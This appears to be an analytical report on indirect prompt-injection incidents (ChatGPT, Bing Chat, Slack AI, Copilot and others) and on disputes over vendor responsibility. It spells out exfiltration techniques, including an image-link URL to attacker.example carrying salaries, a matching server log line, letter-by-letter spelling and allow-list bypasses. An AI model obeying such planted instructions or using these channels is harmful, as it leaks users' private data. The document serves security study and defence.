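# Prompt injection incidents that crossed company lines, and who took responsibility afterward

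## The parties to an AI agent and how an outsider's text moves between them

An AI agent is a program in which a large language model reads material and acts on it through other software, such as by searching a mailbox, editing a file or posting a comment. Usually one company trains the model, another builds the application around it, and others supply the connections to email, documents or code. In a prompt injection attack, someone writes instructions into text that the model will read, and the model carries them out. Private data can then reach a stranger even though every company's part worked as designed. Since 2023 this has happened often enough, mostly in researchers' demonstrations but sometimes to real victims, that the companies involved have had to argue about who is responsible.

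### Why a model confuses data with instructions

*Explaining prompt injection* (Rijo, 2026) traces the first private report to May 2022, when a firm called Preamble described the flaw to OpenAI. That September, the programmer Simon Willison named it prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which a visitor types part of a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Programmers can reliably prevent SQL injection by fixing the structure of the command before inserting the visitor's words, so that the database cannot read those words as a command.

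The fix for SQL injection, separating code from data, can't be applied to language models. Before each answer, the application assembles a prompt from the developer's standing instructions, the conversation so far, tool descriptions, and any pages or emails the tools have returned. The model receives all of this as one sequence of tokens, the word fragments it processes. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, wrote in the centre's December 2025 article *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that inside the model "there is only ever 'next token'". *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) attributes the difference to SQL having a grammar that lets a parser separate code from data, while natural language has no grammar that would allow this.

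Developers use role tags to mark which parts of a prompt come from the user and which from a tool, and providers train their models to give the user's words more authority. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) examined how models represent these roles internally. The researchers wrapped identical passages of web text in each of five role tags and trained a simple classifier to recognize the tag from the model's internal activity alone. Because the words were the same under every tag, the classifier could learn only the tag's effect on that activity. When text sounded like a user but carried the tag for tool output, the classifier rated it 79 to 88 percent "user" in three of the models. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the attack succeeded 2 percent of the time where this confusion was lowest and 70 percent where it was highest. On this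 account, a command on a web page works because it sounds like something a user would type.

Better training might reduce the confusion, but *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that it cannot eliminate it in models that represent instructions and data in the same mathematical space with no enforced separation between the two. Current models fit that description, but the proof does not rule out eliminating the confusion with a different architecture.

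In *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023) pointed out that an attacker can manipulate a model without ever touching the system, whereas most people had at first pictured the attacker tricking a chatbot in their own session. They named this indirect prompt injection. The model obeys instructions hidden in content it reads, such as a message or web page, as if the user had given them. The attacker can leave the text on a public page for a search to retrieve, send it by email, or place it in a code repository. The team demonstrated the attack on Microsoft's Bing Chat, whose sidebar could read the page open in the browser, and steered its answers with text invisible to the human reader. The paper also listed possible consequences, including stolen data, fraud, and emails that make an assistant forward the attack to the next victim. That list was partly a forecast,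 and much of it has since happened in products.

### Where the defenses stand in 2026

Models have become much harder to hijack. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that the share of indirect injections withstood in the company's automated tests rose from 96.23 to 99.79 percent. Gray Swan, a commercial developer of such tests, tried 1,810 selected attacks on GPT-6 Astra and estimated that an attacker allowed 15 attempts per scenario would succeed 8.5 percent of the time, against 27.0 percent for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic's Opus 5 had already reached 2.0 percent within 15 attempts, according to benchmark figures reproduced in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026). The two sets of figures are only roughly comparable, since GPT-5.6 Sol scores 20.0 percent in Schneier's and 27.0 percent in OpenAI's.

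*What happened after 2,000 people tried to hack my AI assistant* (Willison, 2026) describes a public challenge in which Fernando Irarrázaval invited strangers to email his AI assistant and try to extract a secret from it. The assistant ran on Opus 4.6, which was no longer the newest model, and all of the roughly 6,000 attempts failed. Willison took this as a sign that training models to resist prompt injection works, but said he would still not run a system in which a successful injection could do irreversible damage.

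That reading seems right. OpenAI's 99.79 percent amounts to roughly one failure in 480 attempts, which would be good enough for many purposes if the failures were random. But attackers can study what their last email did and send another for almost nothing.

The protection also depends on the product built around the model. In September 2026 Anthropic published tests of Claude Fable 5.1 inside its own product Claude Cowork, with ten attempts in each of 110 browser scenarios. Without extra safeguards, 2.64 percent of attempts succeeded. With an injection detector and a second check on each action switched on, none did. Another company that builds an application on the same model cannot assume it will block every attempt unless it has comparable safeguards. The testers also reused attacks they had developed against an older model, Opus 4.7, so the results don't show how well the current safeguards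 would stop attacks designed to defeat them. Of the 29 attacks that succeeded without the extra safeguards, 21 did so after the session had switched to a fallback model, so a product's protection may depend on more than one model.

Opinion is divided on whether prompt injection can be solved. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in 129 browser scenarios, but also notes that OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that the problem may never be fully solved. *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* (Poireault, 2026) reports that Ariel Fogel, a contributor to the software security project OWASP, called it an unsolved architectural problem in June 2026. Fogel works for Pillar Security, an AI security vendor with a commercial interest in that view, but David C, who has no product to sell, reached much the same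 conclusion. More training is not a sure remedy. *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026) covers research in which training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack. Criminals have also begun to build tools for indirect injection, according to *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026).

### Five parties and one job application

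David C illustrates indirect injection with a recruiter who uses software to score CVs and an applicant who hides a line in their CV telling the model to approve it. With a few additions, this example includes every party that matters in the later incidents.

The *model provider* trains and serves the language model. The *deployer* builds the recruiting assistant on that model and runs it. A *tool vendor* supplies the connector the assistant uses to open the company's personnel files. The *platform*, here a job board, carries the applicants' CVs to the recruiter. The recruiter is the *user*, who connected the personnel files to the assistant and clicked "allow" when it asked for permission.

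Suppose now that an applicant wants the company's salary list. The leak could go like this:

1. The applicant uploads a CV to the job board with instructions in white text on a white background.
2. The recruiter asks the assistant to summarize the week's applications, and the application copies the whole CV, white text included, into the prompt.
3. The model follows the hidden instructions and requests the salary list. The connector checks that the recruiter may see the list, which is true, and returns it.
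4. The model writes its summary and adds an image whose web address contains the salaries. The assistant's window loads the image automatically, and by doing so sends the salaries to the applicant's server.

The recruiter sees a summary, perhaps with a broken image in it. Afterward, the job board can point out that it delivered a document, which is its normal function. The tool vendor's permission check worked, and the deployer's window displayed an image. The model provider never promised that its model would resist every injection, and the recruiter only asked for a summary.

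Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, attributed leaks of this kind to a combination of three things: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. An attacker can turn an agent that has all three against its user. In the recruiter's office, each came from a different party. The tool vendor's connector provided the private data, the job board provided the untrusted content, and the deployer's window provided the exfiltration channel, meaning any route by which private data can reach an attacker. A link that the user clicks or a public comment would also have worked as the channel.

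Removing any one part of the trifecta prevents the leak. Willison listed fourteen products, from ChatGPT to Slack, in which researchers had found such leaks between April 2023 and February 2025, and observed that the vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, mostly by blocking the route by which data could leave. This fix works only when a vendor controls that route. Users who combine tools from several suppliers may assemble the trifecta themselves, and in Willison's view the vendors then can do nothing to protect them. Willison's *GitHub MCP Exploited* describes a single connector from GitHub, the code-hosting company, that supplied all three parts, whereas the earlier worry had been about combining separate tools that each supplied one.

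Under Meta's "Rule of Two", a design rule based on the same idea, an agent should have no more than two of the three properties in any session that runs without human approval. Fogel considers the rule a useful way to limit damage but warns that researchers have already shown attacks that need only two of them.

### Connectors, build pipelines and vulnerability records

AI agents often combine different companies' tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. An MCP server is a program that offers such tools, which might search a mailbox, read a calendar, or run commands on the user's computer. Because all MCP servers follow the same standard, a user can attach servers from several makers to one agent, and no maker needs to know which others are present.

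An outsider's text can also reach an AI agent through a software project. On GitHub, anyone with an account can usually file an "issue", a public note reporting a bug or requesting a feature, in a public project. GitHub Actions, the company's automation service, can run a series of steps in response to events like this, for example to test new code or publish a new version. These build pipelines often hold secret keys that prove the project's identity when it publishes software. If a project adds an AI agent to sort incoming issues, the same model may have access to both a stranger's text and the project's keys. A stolen publishing key is worse than most stolen documents because whoever holds it can send altered software to everyone who installs the next update.

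Researchers who find a flaw normally report it privately. The flaw may then get a CVE, a public identifier that scanners and security teams use to track a software vulnerability. Authorized organizations, many of them software vendors, assign CVEs under shared rules. CVSS is a standard severity score from 0 to 10 that takes into account how easily an attacker can use the flaw and how much damage results. EchoLeak, a 2025 flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, let an attacker extract data by sending a single crafted email, without the victim clicking anything. It is listed as CVE-2025-32711 and scored 9.3. Many companies also run a bug bounty, a program that pays outside researchers for reporting flaws within a scope the company sets. If a company leaves prompt injection out of that scope, a researcher who reports it may be thanked but not paid.

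This whole system developed around flaws in one product with one owner, but it isn't obvious whose product is at fault in the salary leak.

### What a party can claim, and what it can reply

A *component claim* describes one party's part of the system, such as "The connector returns only files that the recruiter may open." An *end-to-end claim* describes the assembled system, such as "No applicant's CV can cause those files to reach the applicant." In the example, the tool vendor made only the component claim, which is true even though the end-to-end claim is false.

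A party that receives a report of such a leak can respond in several ways. It can fix its own part of the system. For example, the deployer might stop its window from loading images from unknown addresses, which blocks that route for every customer at once. It can add an optional setting, such as a switch that makes the connector request confirmation before opening salary data, but this helps only those who find the switch and turn it on. Or it can add a warning to the documentation that advises customers not to combine personnel files with documents from strangers, which leaves the software unchanged and means users have to protect themselves.

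The remaining reply is a disclaimer, in which the party says the flaw is not its to fix. Disclaimers come in three main versions. The tool vendor may call the behavior intended, since a connector is meant to return files to an authorized user. The model provider may call it architectural, arguing that all language models have this weakness and the deployer has to build around it. The third version is that the user's configuration allowed it, since the recruiter connected the personnel files and clicked "allow". Each of these can be accurate, and a company may well issue one while quietly fixing the flaw. In practice, the recruiter needs to know whether anything changed before the next CV arrived.

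## Chat assistants that leaked data through image links, 2023 to 2026

In the recruiter's office, the salaries left the company inside the web address of an image. Researchers found in the spring of 2023 that ChatGPT and Bing Chat could leak data this way, and the same flaw has since turned up in dozens of AI products. The same researcher reported it to Microsoft and OpenAI one day apart. Microsoft restricted images in Bing Chat within about two months. OpenAI first replied that it planned no change, then issued a fix in December and spent more than two years correcting that fix.

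### How a picture carries data out

Chat assistants usually format their answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation in which asterisks make text bold and a short pattern of brackets around a web address inserts an image. The model writes only the notation, and the chat window converts it into a formatted page. To display an image, the chat window requests the file from the server at that address. The server receives the whole address, including anything after a question mark, where websites normally put data such as search terms.

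The hidden text in the applicant's CV relied on the way chat windows load images. If planted text gets the model to write an image link with private data at the end of its address, the window sends that data to the image's server when it requests the image, without the user clicking anything.

Suppose the attacker owns the made-up domain attacker.example, and the model has written this address for a picture:

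`https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=Okafor+61000+Lind+58500`

The attacker's server then adds a line like this to its log:

`203.0.113.7 - - [14/May/2023:10:22:31 +0000] "GET /logo.png?q=Okafor+61000+Lind+58500 HTTP/1.1" 200 472`

The line records the network address of the computer that asked for the picture, the time, and the requested path, which contains two employees' salaries. The 200 means the server answered normally, and 472 is the size of the answer in bytes. The attacker only has to read the log. Johann Rehberger, an independent security researcher, printed several real lines of this kind in *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* on his blog, Embrace The Red. One from September 2023 contains the start of a test conversation in which a user called Alice mentions liking finance and cookies.

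Rehberger's demonstration against Microsoft's assistant, described in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, used text planted on a web page that the user had open beside the chat. The text instructed the model to announce the injection immediately but write the image link only after two more turns of conversation, to show that the attacker still controlled the chat. The image's URL contained a short summary of the page and the conversation, along with a secret from further down the page. An attacker could have planted the text through an advertisement or a reader's comment.

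Roman Samoilenko found the flaw in ChatGPT a few days before Rehberger did. According to Willison (2023), Samoilenko's attack used a single-pixel image and a website that added instructions to whatever a visitor copied. The attack depended on the visitor pasting the copied text into ChatGPT without checking it.

### Two replies to one report

Rehberger wrote to Microsoft on April 8, 2023 and to OpenAI on April 9. Microsoft acknowledged the problem and set a content security policy for Bing Chat. With such a policy, a website sends the browser a list of the domains from which it may load images and other material. Rehberger found four domains on Bing Chat's list, all belonging to Bing, and the old attacks no longer worked. In his original post, he wrote that Microsoft told him of the fix on June 15, but Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*,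 his later account, dates the fix to May. Microsoft may have announced the fix some weeks after making it.

Text on a web page could still hijack Bing Chat's model under the policy. But a hijacked Bing Chat could no longer send data to an arbitrary server through an image, because the browser loads images only from servers on the policy's list, regardless of what the model writes.

OpenAI replied that displaying Markdown images was a feature and that it planned no changes, according to Rehberger's *ChatGPT Plugins*. It was disclaiming responsibility on the ground that the behavior was intended. That position had some basis while users had to paste in the hostile text themselves, as in Samoilenko's version. Rehberger had told OpenAI during the exchange that plugins would remove that protection, and they did. Plugins, many of them made by other companies, let ChatGPT fetch web pages, read video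 transcripts or look up flights. In one test, a web page fetched through the WebPilot plugin took over the conversation and sent the earlier chat to Rehberger's server. In another, planted text made ChatGPT search for flights through Expedia's plugin without the user asking.

Several companies now had a part in the leak, and Rehberger asked for a security contract for plugins that would settle "Who is responsible for what?" The plugin had fetched the page as requested, OpenAI's interface had displayed an image as designed, and the user had switched the plugin on but had little control over what it did afterward. Rehberger thought OpenAI should have dealt with the risk in the platform instead of leaving it to plugin developers and end users. By September 2023 he could make ChatGPT use a plugin to write the whole conversation into a document or a narrated video, then leak the link to it through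 an image. He sent OpenAI a draft and got an automated response.

Other companies treated the same flaw as theirs to fix. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* records that Anthropic closed it in Claude. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* covers the flaw in Google's studio for developers. Google accepted Rehberger's report 22 minutes after he submitted it and had fixed the flaw by October. Microsoft also fixed a testing area for developers, according to Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*. OpenAI's position was hard to defend as a general view of what chat software does, because these three competitors also displayed Markdown and all decided that a stranger should not be able to choose where the images came from.

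### url_safe and the ways around it

OpenAI began to act in December 2023. The morning after giving a live demonstration with a consenting victim, Rehberger noticed that ChatGPT had changed. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that the web app now sent each image's address to an OpenAI service called url_safe before displaying the image. If the service flagged the address as unsafe, the app did not request the image. Willison (2023) welcomed the change but thought it a bit weird that OpenAI had not just blocked images from outside domains.

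The design had two weaknesses. First, the app on the user's device made the check, so OpenAI had to build it into each app separately. According to Embrace The Red's *AI Domination*, the iPhone and Mac apps didn't get the check until September 2024. Second, nobody outside OpenAI could see how url_safe reached its decisions, whereas anyone can read a content security policy in their own browser. Rehberger tried 36 addresses on his own domain, one for each letter and digit, and url_safe approved nine for no reason he could discover. With those he could spell out short words such as "hi", one image per letter.

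In *From ChatBot To SpyBot*, the security company Imperva worked out part of url_safe's logic. The check approved an address if the same string already appeared in the conversation. The reasoning behind such a rule is good. An attacker writes the planted text without knowing the victim's password, so an address copied exactly from that text can't contain the password.

An attacker can plant one address for every letter and digit and tell the model to load them in the order that spells the password. Imperva also tried a single long address that ended in the whole alphabet. The model cut the address off at the letter to be sent, and the shortened version still passed the check because it matched part of the conversation. A third method used a separate domain for each character, at a dollar or two apiece. In these tests, the attacker had already altered the user's saved instructions rather than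 starting from an ordinary web page. Imperva conceded that taking large amounts of data unnoticed had become much harder.

Trusted domains offered a faster route. In October 2024 Rehberger reported several to OpenAI. He had looked for sites that url_safe approved, that accepted data in an ordinary page request, and that let outsiders read the data they received. GitHub didn't meet the last condition. Rehberger could post instructions there for a hijacked ChatGPT to collect, but only Microsoft, which owns GitHub, can read the server logs. Microsoft's windows.net met all three conditions. Customers who rent storage on Microsoft's cloud get an address on that domain and can inspect the log of every request to their address. An attacker could rent storage and have ChatGPT send whole sentences there.

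Those bypasses were still open when Rehberger published *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* on Embrace The Red in 2025. By then an attacker could obtain more through the leak, because ChatGPT had begun adding extracts from the user's recent conversations to every prompt. A single malicious PDF could therefore expose things the user had discussed on other days. Rehberger asked OpenAI about the fix several times in the month before publishing, got no update, and left the working instructions out of the post.

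Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* describes a similar flaw involving Bing. Tenable, which sells security software, noticed that url_safe always approved addresses on bing.com. Bing's search results use bing.com links that redirect to the listed sites, so any website that Bing has indexed also has an approved address. Tenable sent OpenAI a full report on December 10, 2024, and OpenAI acknowledged it the same day. Tenable asked for an update six times between then and March 4, 2025. OpenAI added one person to the email thread during that period, and the flaw was still open when Tenable published.

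In both cases, OpenAI's url_safe check used the owner of a domain to judge who would receive the data. Microsoft owns windows.net and bing.com, but data sent to those domains could still reach others, because Microsoft rents out space on windows.net and forwards visitors from bing.com to other sites. Both services were working as intended, and nothing in their design limited where data sent to them could end up.

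Tenable's *HackedGPT* (November 2025) explains that nobody can add text to Bing's forwarding links, so a single link can't carry a password. Tenable therefore had Bing index a separate page for each letter and spelled out the data one link at a time.

The same research tested another of OpenAI's precautions. ChatGPT handed web browsing to a second model, which Tenable calls SearchGPT and which could not see the user's memories or past chats. A blog comment could hijack SearchGPT, but SearchGPT had no private data to leak. Tenable's comment therefore told it to end its summary with further instructions. ChatGPT, which had the private data but never read the blog, received those instructions in the summary and followed them.

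All of these leaks were researchers' demonstrations, and none of the reports describes a real victim.

### OpenAI's stronger rule

OpenAI tightened the check in the summer of 2025. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) records that OpenAI told Tenable on July 11 that it had improved the check, and Rehberger dates the measures that stopped his own attacks to around August. These changes may not have stopped every attack. Tenable wrote in November that several of its attacks still worked on ChatGPT 5, and one of its demonstrations on that version leaked data through images.

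By this time, images were not the only way to leak data. ChatGPT's Deep Research feature could open web addresses from OpenAI's own servers, and a content security policy can't block those requests because they don't come from the user's browser. Radware, a vendor that sells security for AI agents, used this to take data from Gmail with a single email in an attack it called ShadowLeak. ThaiCERT's *"ShadowLeak" Vulnerability Exposes Gmail Data via ChatGPT Deep Research* (2025) says that Radware reported it on June 18 and that OpenAI patched it in early August.

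OpenAI then barred ChatGPT from altering any web address it had received. *ZombieAgent*, Radware's follow-up, got around this with the old alphabet method. The attack email contained a ready-made address for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT spelled out the data by opening them one after another, unchanged. Because requests can arrive out of order, Radware made numbered copies of each address to mark each character's position, so a block of ten characters needed 360 addresses. To trigger the attack, the user only had to ask ChatGPT to do something with their inbox. Radware reported the attack on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16.

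On January 28, 2026, OpenAI published *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*, together with a technical paper. Both explain a rule for opening links that no longer depends on who owns the domain. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that records the addresses it finds on the public web, and it has no access to anyone's conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT opens an address on its own, the system looks for that exact address in the crawler's records. If it is there, ChatGPT may load it. If not, the system tells ChatGPT to try another site or warns the user that the link may include information from the conversation.

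The rule works because an address that the model has just made up to hold someone's salary did not exist before the conversation, so the crawler can't have seen it. OpenAI said it rejected lists of trusted sites because many legitimate sites forward visitors elsewhere, as Tenable had shown with Bing, and because strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

An attacker can still spell out private data using pages that crawlers have already recorded. Rehberger points out that anyone with a fairly large blog already has 36 such pages, one for each letter and digit. The planted text only has to specify which page stands for which character. With a few thousand pages, each could stand for a whole word. No single address contains anything private, because the information is in which addresses the model requests and in what order. According to Rehberger, OpenAI's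 paper describes this leak too. He suggested preventing an agent from opening the same address twice in a session, which would make repeated letters harder to send.

OpenAI promises only to stop the agent from quietly leaking a user's data "through the URL itself", and on a literal reading the alphabet method doesn't break that promise. OpenAI's post also says that the rule does not make web pages trustworthy or browsing safe in every sense. This component claim is useful because readers can learn from it what the check does and, fairly plainly, what it leaves open. In 2023 OpenAI had made no claim about pictures, so it could not be held to one.

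OpenAI has also become more open about why it needs such a check. *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* says the check is for cases where planted text has already misled the agent, and lists the products that use it, including the Atlas browser and Deep Research. OpenAI has also added an optional Lockdown Mode for users who want more protection, which Willison (2026) describes as limiting the outbound requests that could carry data away.

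Rehberger's main remaining worry was that some OpenAI developers might not know about the check, so some product might not use it. At the time, OpenAI was already dealing with a case in which one of its own windows displayed images without an adequate check.

### The log viewer that undid another company's fix

Many businesses build their own chat windows on OpenAI's models through its API, which lets their software send prompts and receive answers. These chat windows don't automatically get ChatGPT's protections. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested whether planted text could make models leak a secret. The ChatGPT product never leaked it in 48 valid trials, while the model reached through the API leaked it in up to 100 percent of trials. The researchers could not see inside the product and did not say what prevented the leaks, but businesses that use the API need to add their own defenses.

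PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes an attack on a mock tool of the kind banks use to check a new customer's identity. PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of the AI products companies buy from other vendors, built the tool itself. The tool combined the customer's passport details and finances with material from six sources, one of which contained text from the internet with hidden instructions. When a bank employee asked the assistant about the customer, the model's answer included an image link whose address contained the customer's data. A second model, which reviewed every answer, flagged and blocked this one, and no image appeared in the tool.

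A developer is likely to look into a flagged answer, and the natural place to do so is OpenAI's dashboard, which keeps logs of the conversations. The dashboard rendered the logged answers as Markdown, including images, so opening the log sent the request that the application had blocked. That request delivered the passport number and credit history to the attacker's log.

The same thing could happen with other defenses. If an application stripped images from answers or displayed only plain text, the original answer would still be in OpenAI's log. PromptArmor showed an answer from the search assistant Perplexity that looked empty after the software had removed an image. A confused user might click "thumbs down", which would send the conversation for review. PromptArmor presented this as a possibility and did not report that Perplexity had lost any data. It also found the same unsafe display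 in several of OpenAI's preview and testing screens and in a starter application that OpenAI gives to developers.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on November 17, 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that receives and sorts bug reports for OpenAI. PromptArmor supplied step-by-step instructions on November 20 and answered questions on November 24, 25 and 26. Bugcrowd closed the report as not applicable on December 4. PromptArmor then published its findings, and OpenAI said it had not seen the report, because Bugcrowd had handled it. OpenAI confirmed the flaw, reopened the report on January 22, 2026 and said a fix was underway. PromptArmor's timeline ends there and does not record a completed fix.

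The application's developer could truthfully say that the banking tool never displayed the dangerous answer. Nobody had promised that it wouldn't appear elsewhere. The developer couldn't have, because the other screen belonged to OpenAI, and it isn't clear that a developer would have thought to ask. Only OpenAI could close this route for every customer at once. Google and Microsoft had accepted reports about their own developer tools in 2023, so treating such a screen as a security problem was not new. The contractor that first refused the report had exchanged messages with the finder four times after it was submitted.

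### The same leak in other products

The company that displays a model's output can stop leaks through image links without solving prompt injection. Microsoft did so in Bing Chat when models were far easier to hijack than they are now. Deployers can use this fix even when they can't retrain the model, because they control their own interfaces. That control also makes "this is intended behavior" a weak reply from the company that runs the interface. But the company has to find every place where the output appears and allow only safe addresses, and later cases show companies failing at both.

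Microsoft responded promptly in 2023 but had the same problem again. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* attributes two later Copilot flaws, EchoLeak in 2025 and SearchLeak in 2026, to image links that the model wrote. In May 2026, Willison (2026) covered a third case, in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork. That agent could email its own user without asking permission, and the emails could contain external images. When the user opened an email, the request for an image could send the attacker links for downloading files from the user's OneDrive. As with OpenAI's logs, the leak happened in a separate window from the assistant.

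Superhuman, an email application, allowed images from docs.google.com. Google Forms runs on that domain and saves answers included in a web address, so a planted email could make the assistant submit the contents of dozens of other emails to an attacker's form. Willison credits Superhuman with treating the report as urgent and fixing the flaw. Salesforce's list of allowed domains included one that had expired, and researchers bought it.

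Google's response to a similar report was less clear. In November 2025, a researcher who had found that Google's coding tool Antigravity leaked data through Markdown images said the company had marked the report as intended behavior. But Google's bug bounty page for Antigravity listed data theft through prompt injection as a known issue that the company was working to fix, and Google paid no reward for reports of it.

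Blocking image links leaves other routes open, such as links that the user clicks and messaging programs that preview links automatically. In January 2026, PromptArmor extracted files from Anthropic's Claude Cowork, which allowed outgoing connections only to listed domains. It did so by having the agent upload the files to Anthropic's own service under the attacker's account.

Ayush Paul found a leak in Claude's chat product that used ordinary web links instead of images. Anthropic had restricted web_fetch, Claude's tool for opening web pages, so that the model could not make up addresses. In its developer documentation in September 2025, the company listed the addresses the tool could open, which were those from the user, from search results and from pages it had already fetched, and warned that some risk remained. Paul used the permission to open links from fetched pages. He built a website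 that told Claude it had to identify its user by browsing an alphabetical directory, letter by letter, with each page supplying the links for the next step. The site showed these instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made them harder for anyone else to notice. By following the links, Claude gave away the user's name, home city and employer.

Willison (2026) reported in July that Anthropic did not pay Paul a bounty, saying its own staff had already found the vulnerability. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links on the pages it fetches.

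## Slack AI in 2024, and the link previews that later removed the click

In August 2024, PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* showed how one member of a company's Slack workspace could make the built-in assistant give a colleague a link containing that colleague's own secret. The link sent nothing until the colleague clicked it, so it seems a weaker exfiltration channel than an image that loads by itself. Slack first replied that the behavior was intended, then patched it on the day the research came out. That same week, Rehberger warned that messaging apps often open links automatically to prepare a preview, so data can leave without a click if an AI agent posts the link.

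### What Slack had claimed

Slack AI lets people ask questions about their company's messages in ordinary language. Any member of a company's Slack workspace can search and read its public channels, including ones they have never joined, but only members of a private channel can read it.

Slack (2025) explained the assistant's design in a post first published on its engineering blog in April 2024, four months before the dispute. When a user asks a question, Slack searches with that user's permissions, copies the relevant messages into a prompt and sends the prompt to a language model, which keeps nothing afterward. The assistant therefore can't show anyone a message that ordinary search would hide from them. Only the person who asked sees the answer.

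The same post makes a broader promise, "Customer data never leaves Slack," but the explanation beneath it covers only hosting. Slack ran its models inside its own section of Amazon's cloud so that the company supplying a model could not keep customers' messages or train on them. This restricts the model provider's access but does not stop a link in an answer from carrying data out of Slack. Slack's help page now says that data never leaves "Slack-controlled infrastructure", but a customer who took either version literally would still expect more than the hosting arrangement can deliver.

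### One question and two messages

PromptArmor staged the attack with a made-up service and an API key, a secret code that lets software use a service. It went like this:

1. A developer saves the key in a private channel that has no other members.
2. The attacker, who has an account in the same workspace, creates a public channel and posts a message there. Nobody else joins. The message names the service and tells the model to answer questions about its key with an error notice and a link, adding the key to the end of the link's address.
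3. The developer asks Slack AI for the key. The search finds both messages, because the developer may read both, and Slack puts them into one prompt.
4. Slack AI answers that the message failed to load and offers a link to "reauthenticate". The address behind those words leads to the attacker's server and ends in the key.
5. The developer clicks, and the attacker reads the key in the server's log.

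The attacker never enters the private channel and doesn't need to know the key. But the planted message named the service, so this attacker had to guess what somebody would ask about. PromptArmor suspected that a more general message would also work, because its search had turned up other messages about API keys, but it did not demonstrate this.

Slack AI's answers include numbered citations to the messages behind them. In this case, the only citation pointed to the developer's own private channel. The attacker's message had produced the wording and the link, but Slack AI did not cite it, and it did not appear on the first page of search results. A developer who grew suspicious after clicking would have found little evidence beyond a reference to their own note.

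In a second demonstration, the planted message made Slack AI return a phishing link to anyone who asked for a summary of a particular colleague's messages, such as their manager's. This time the citation led to the attacker's channel. PromptArmor concluded that the citations were more or less random, so they could expose an attacker but weren't a reliable way for investigators to find the source.

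Slack AI searched only messages until August 14, the day of PromptArmor's report, when it began to draw on uploaded files and connected drives too. PromptArmor argued that an attacker might no longer need a Slack account, because they could hide instructions in a PDF in white text and wait for an employee to download it and upload it to Slack. PromptArmor had finished testing before the change, so it inferred this variant without trying it. The inference is reasonable, since text from a file ends up in the same kind of prompt as text from a message, but whether the attack would have worked remains unknown. The answer matters because Slack's later defense of its product relied on the attacker having an account.

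### "Intended behavior"

Slack asked for more information on August 15. PromptArmor sent videos and screenshots that day and said it intended to publish because of the flaw's severity and the new file feature. They exchanged another question and answer on Friday, August 16. On Monday, August 19, Slack replied that it found the evidence insufficient. It said the information in the first video came from a public channel, which any member can search without joining it, and called this "intended behavior."

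That was true as a statement about search permissions. The developer was allowed to read both the attacker's message and the private note, and Slack AI showed the answer only to the developer. But PromptArmor was complaining about the two being combined in the same prompt. Checking who may read each message can't stop the model from following instructions in one message about what to do with another, and nothing else in Slack's design prevented that.

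Slack's reply also fits poorly with PromptArmor's published account, in which the key is in a private channel. Slack's reviewers may have mistaken the attacker's planted message for the data that PromptArmor said was at risk. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the nature and severity of the problem. PromptArmor was kinder, crediting Slack's security team with quick answers and a real attempt to understand, and it attributed the disagreement to how new prompt injection was.

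Slack received PromptArmor's report six days before PromptArmor published on August 20, and spent that time deciding whether there was anything to fix. It deployed a patch on the day of publication, which suggests that the engineering was easier than the decision.

### Phishing or theft

In a statement on August 21, Slack (2024) said that under "very limited and specific circumstances" someone with an existing account in the same workspace "could phish users for certain data". PromptArmor, describing the same flaw, had written that attackers could steal anything a user put in a private channel.

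Slack was right about the conditions. In the version PromptArmor tested, the attacker needed an account, and the victim had to ask a question that retrieved both messages and then click a link. The word "anything" also goes further than the demonstration, which extracted one key that the attacker's message had asked for.

PromptArmor described the mechanism better. In ordinary phishing, the victim reaches a fake page and types in a password, so a careful person can still stop before typing. Here the link's address already contained the secret, so clicking it was enough to send the secret to the attacker. ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages* includes a fuller statement in which Slack described an attacker "crafting a phishing link". The attacker supplied the template, but Slack AI filled in the secret and presented the link as its own error message.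 Employees who distrust links from strangers would have had little reason to distrust this one.

The requirement for an account also limits the risk less than Slack's wording implies, because companies use private channels to keep information from other people in the same workspace, who already have accounts. The risk may be small in a firm of ten people, but in a workspace with thousands of accounts, an attacker needs only one of them. PromptArmor pointed to earlier leaks through Slack at Disney, Uber and other companies.

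### The patch and the model behind it

Slack said it had no evidence of unauthorized access to customer data, but it did not explain what the patch changed. It might have removed links from answers, restricted the addresses they could point to, or screened messages before they reached the model. Each would protect against different attacks, and customers could not tell from the statement whether the patch covered instructions hidden in files.

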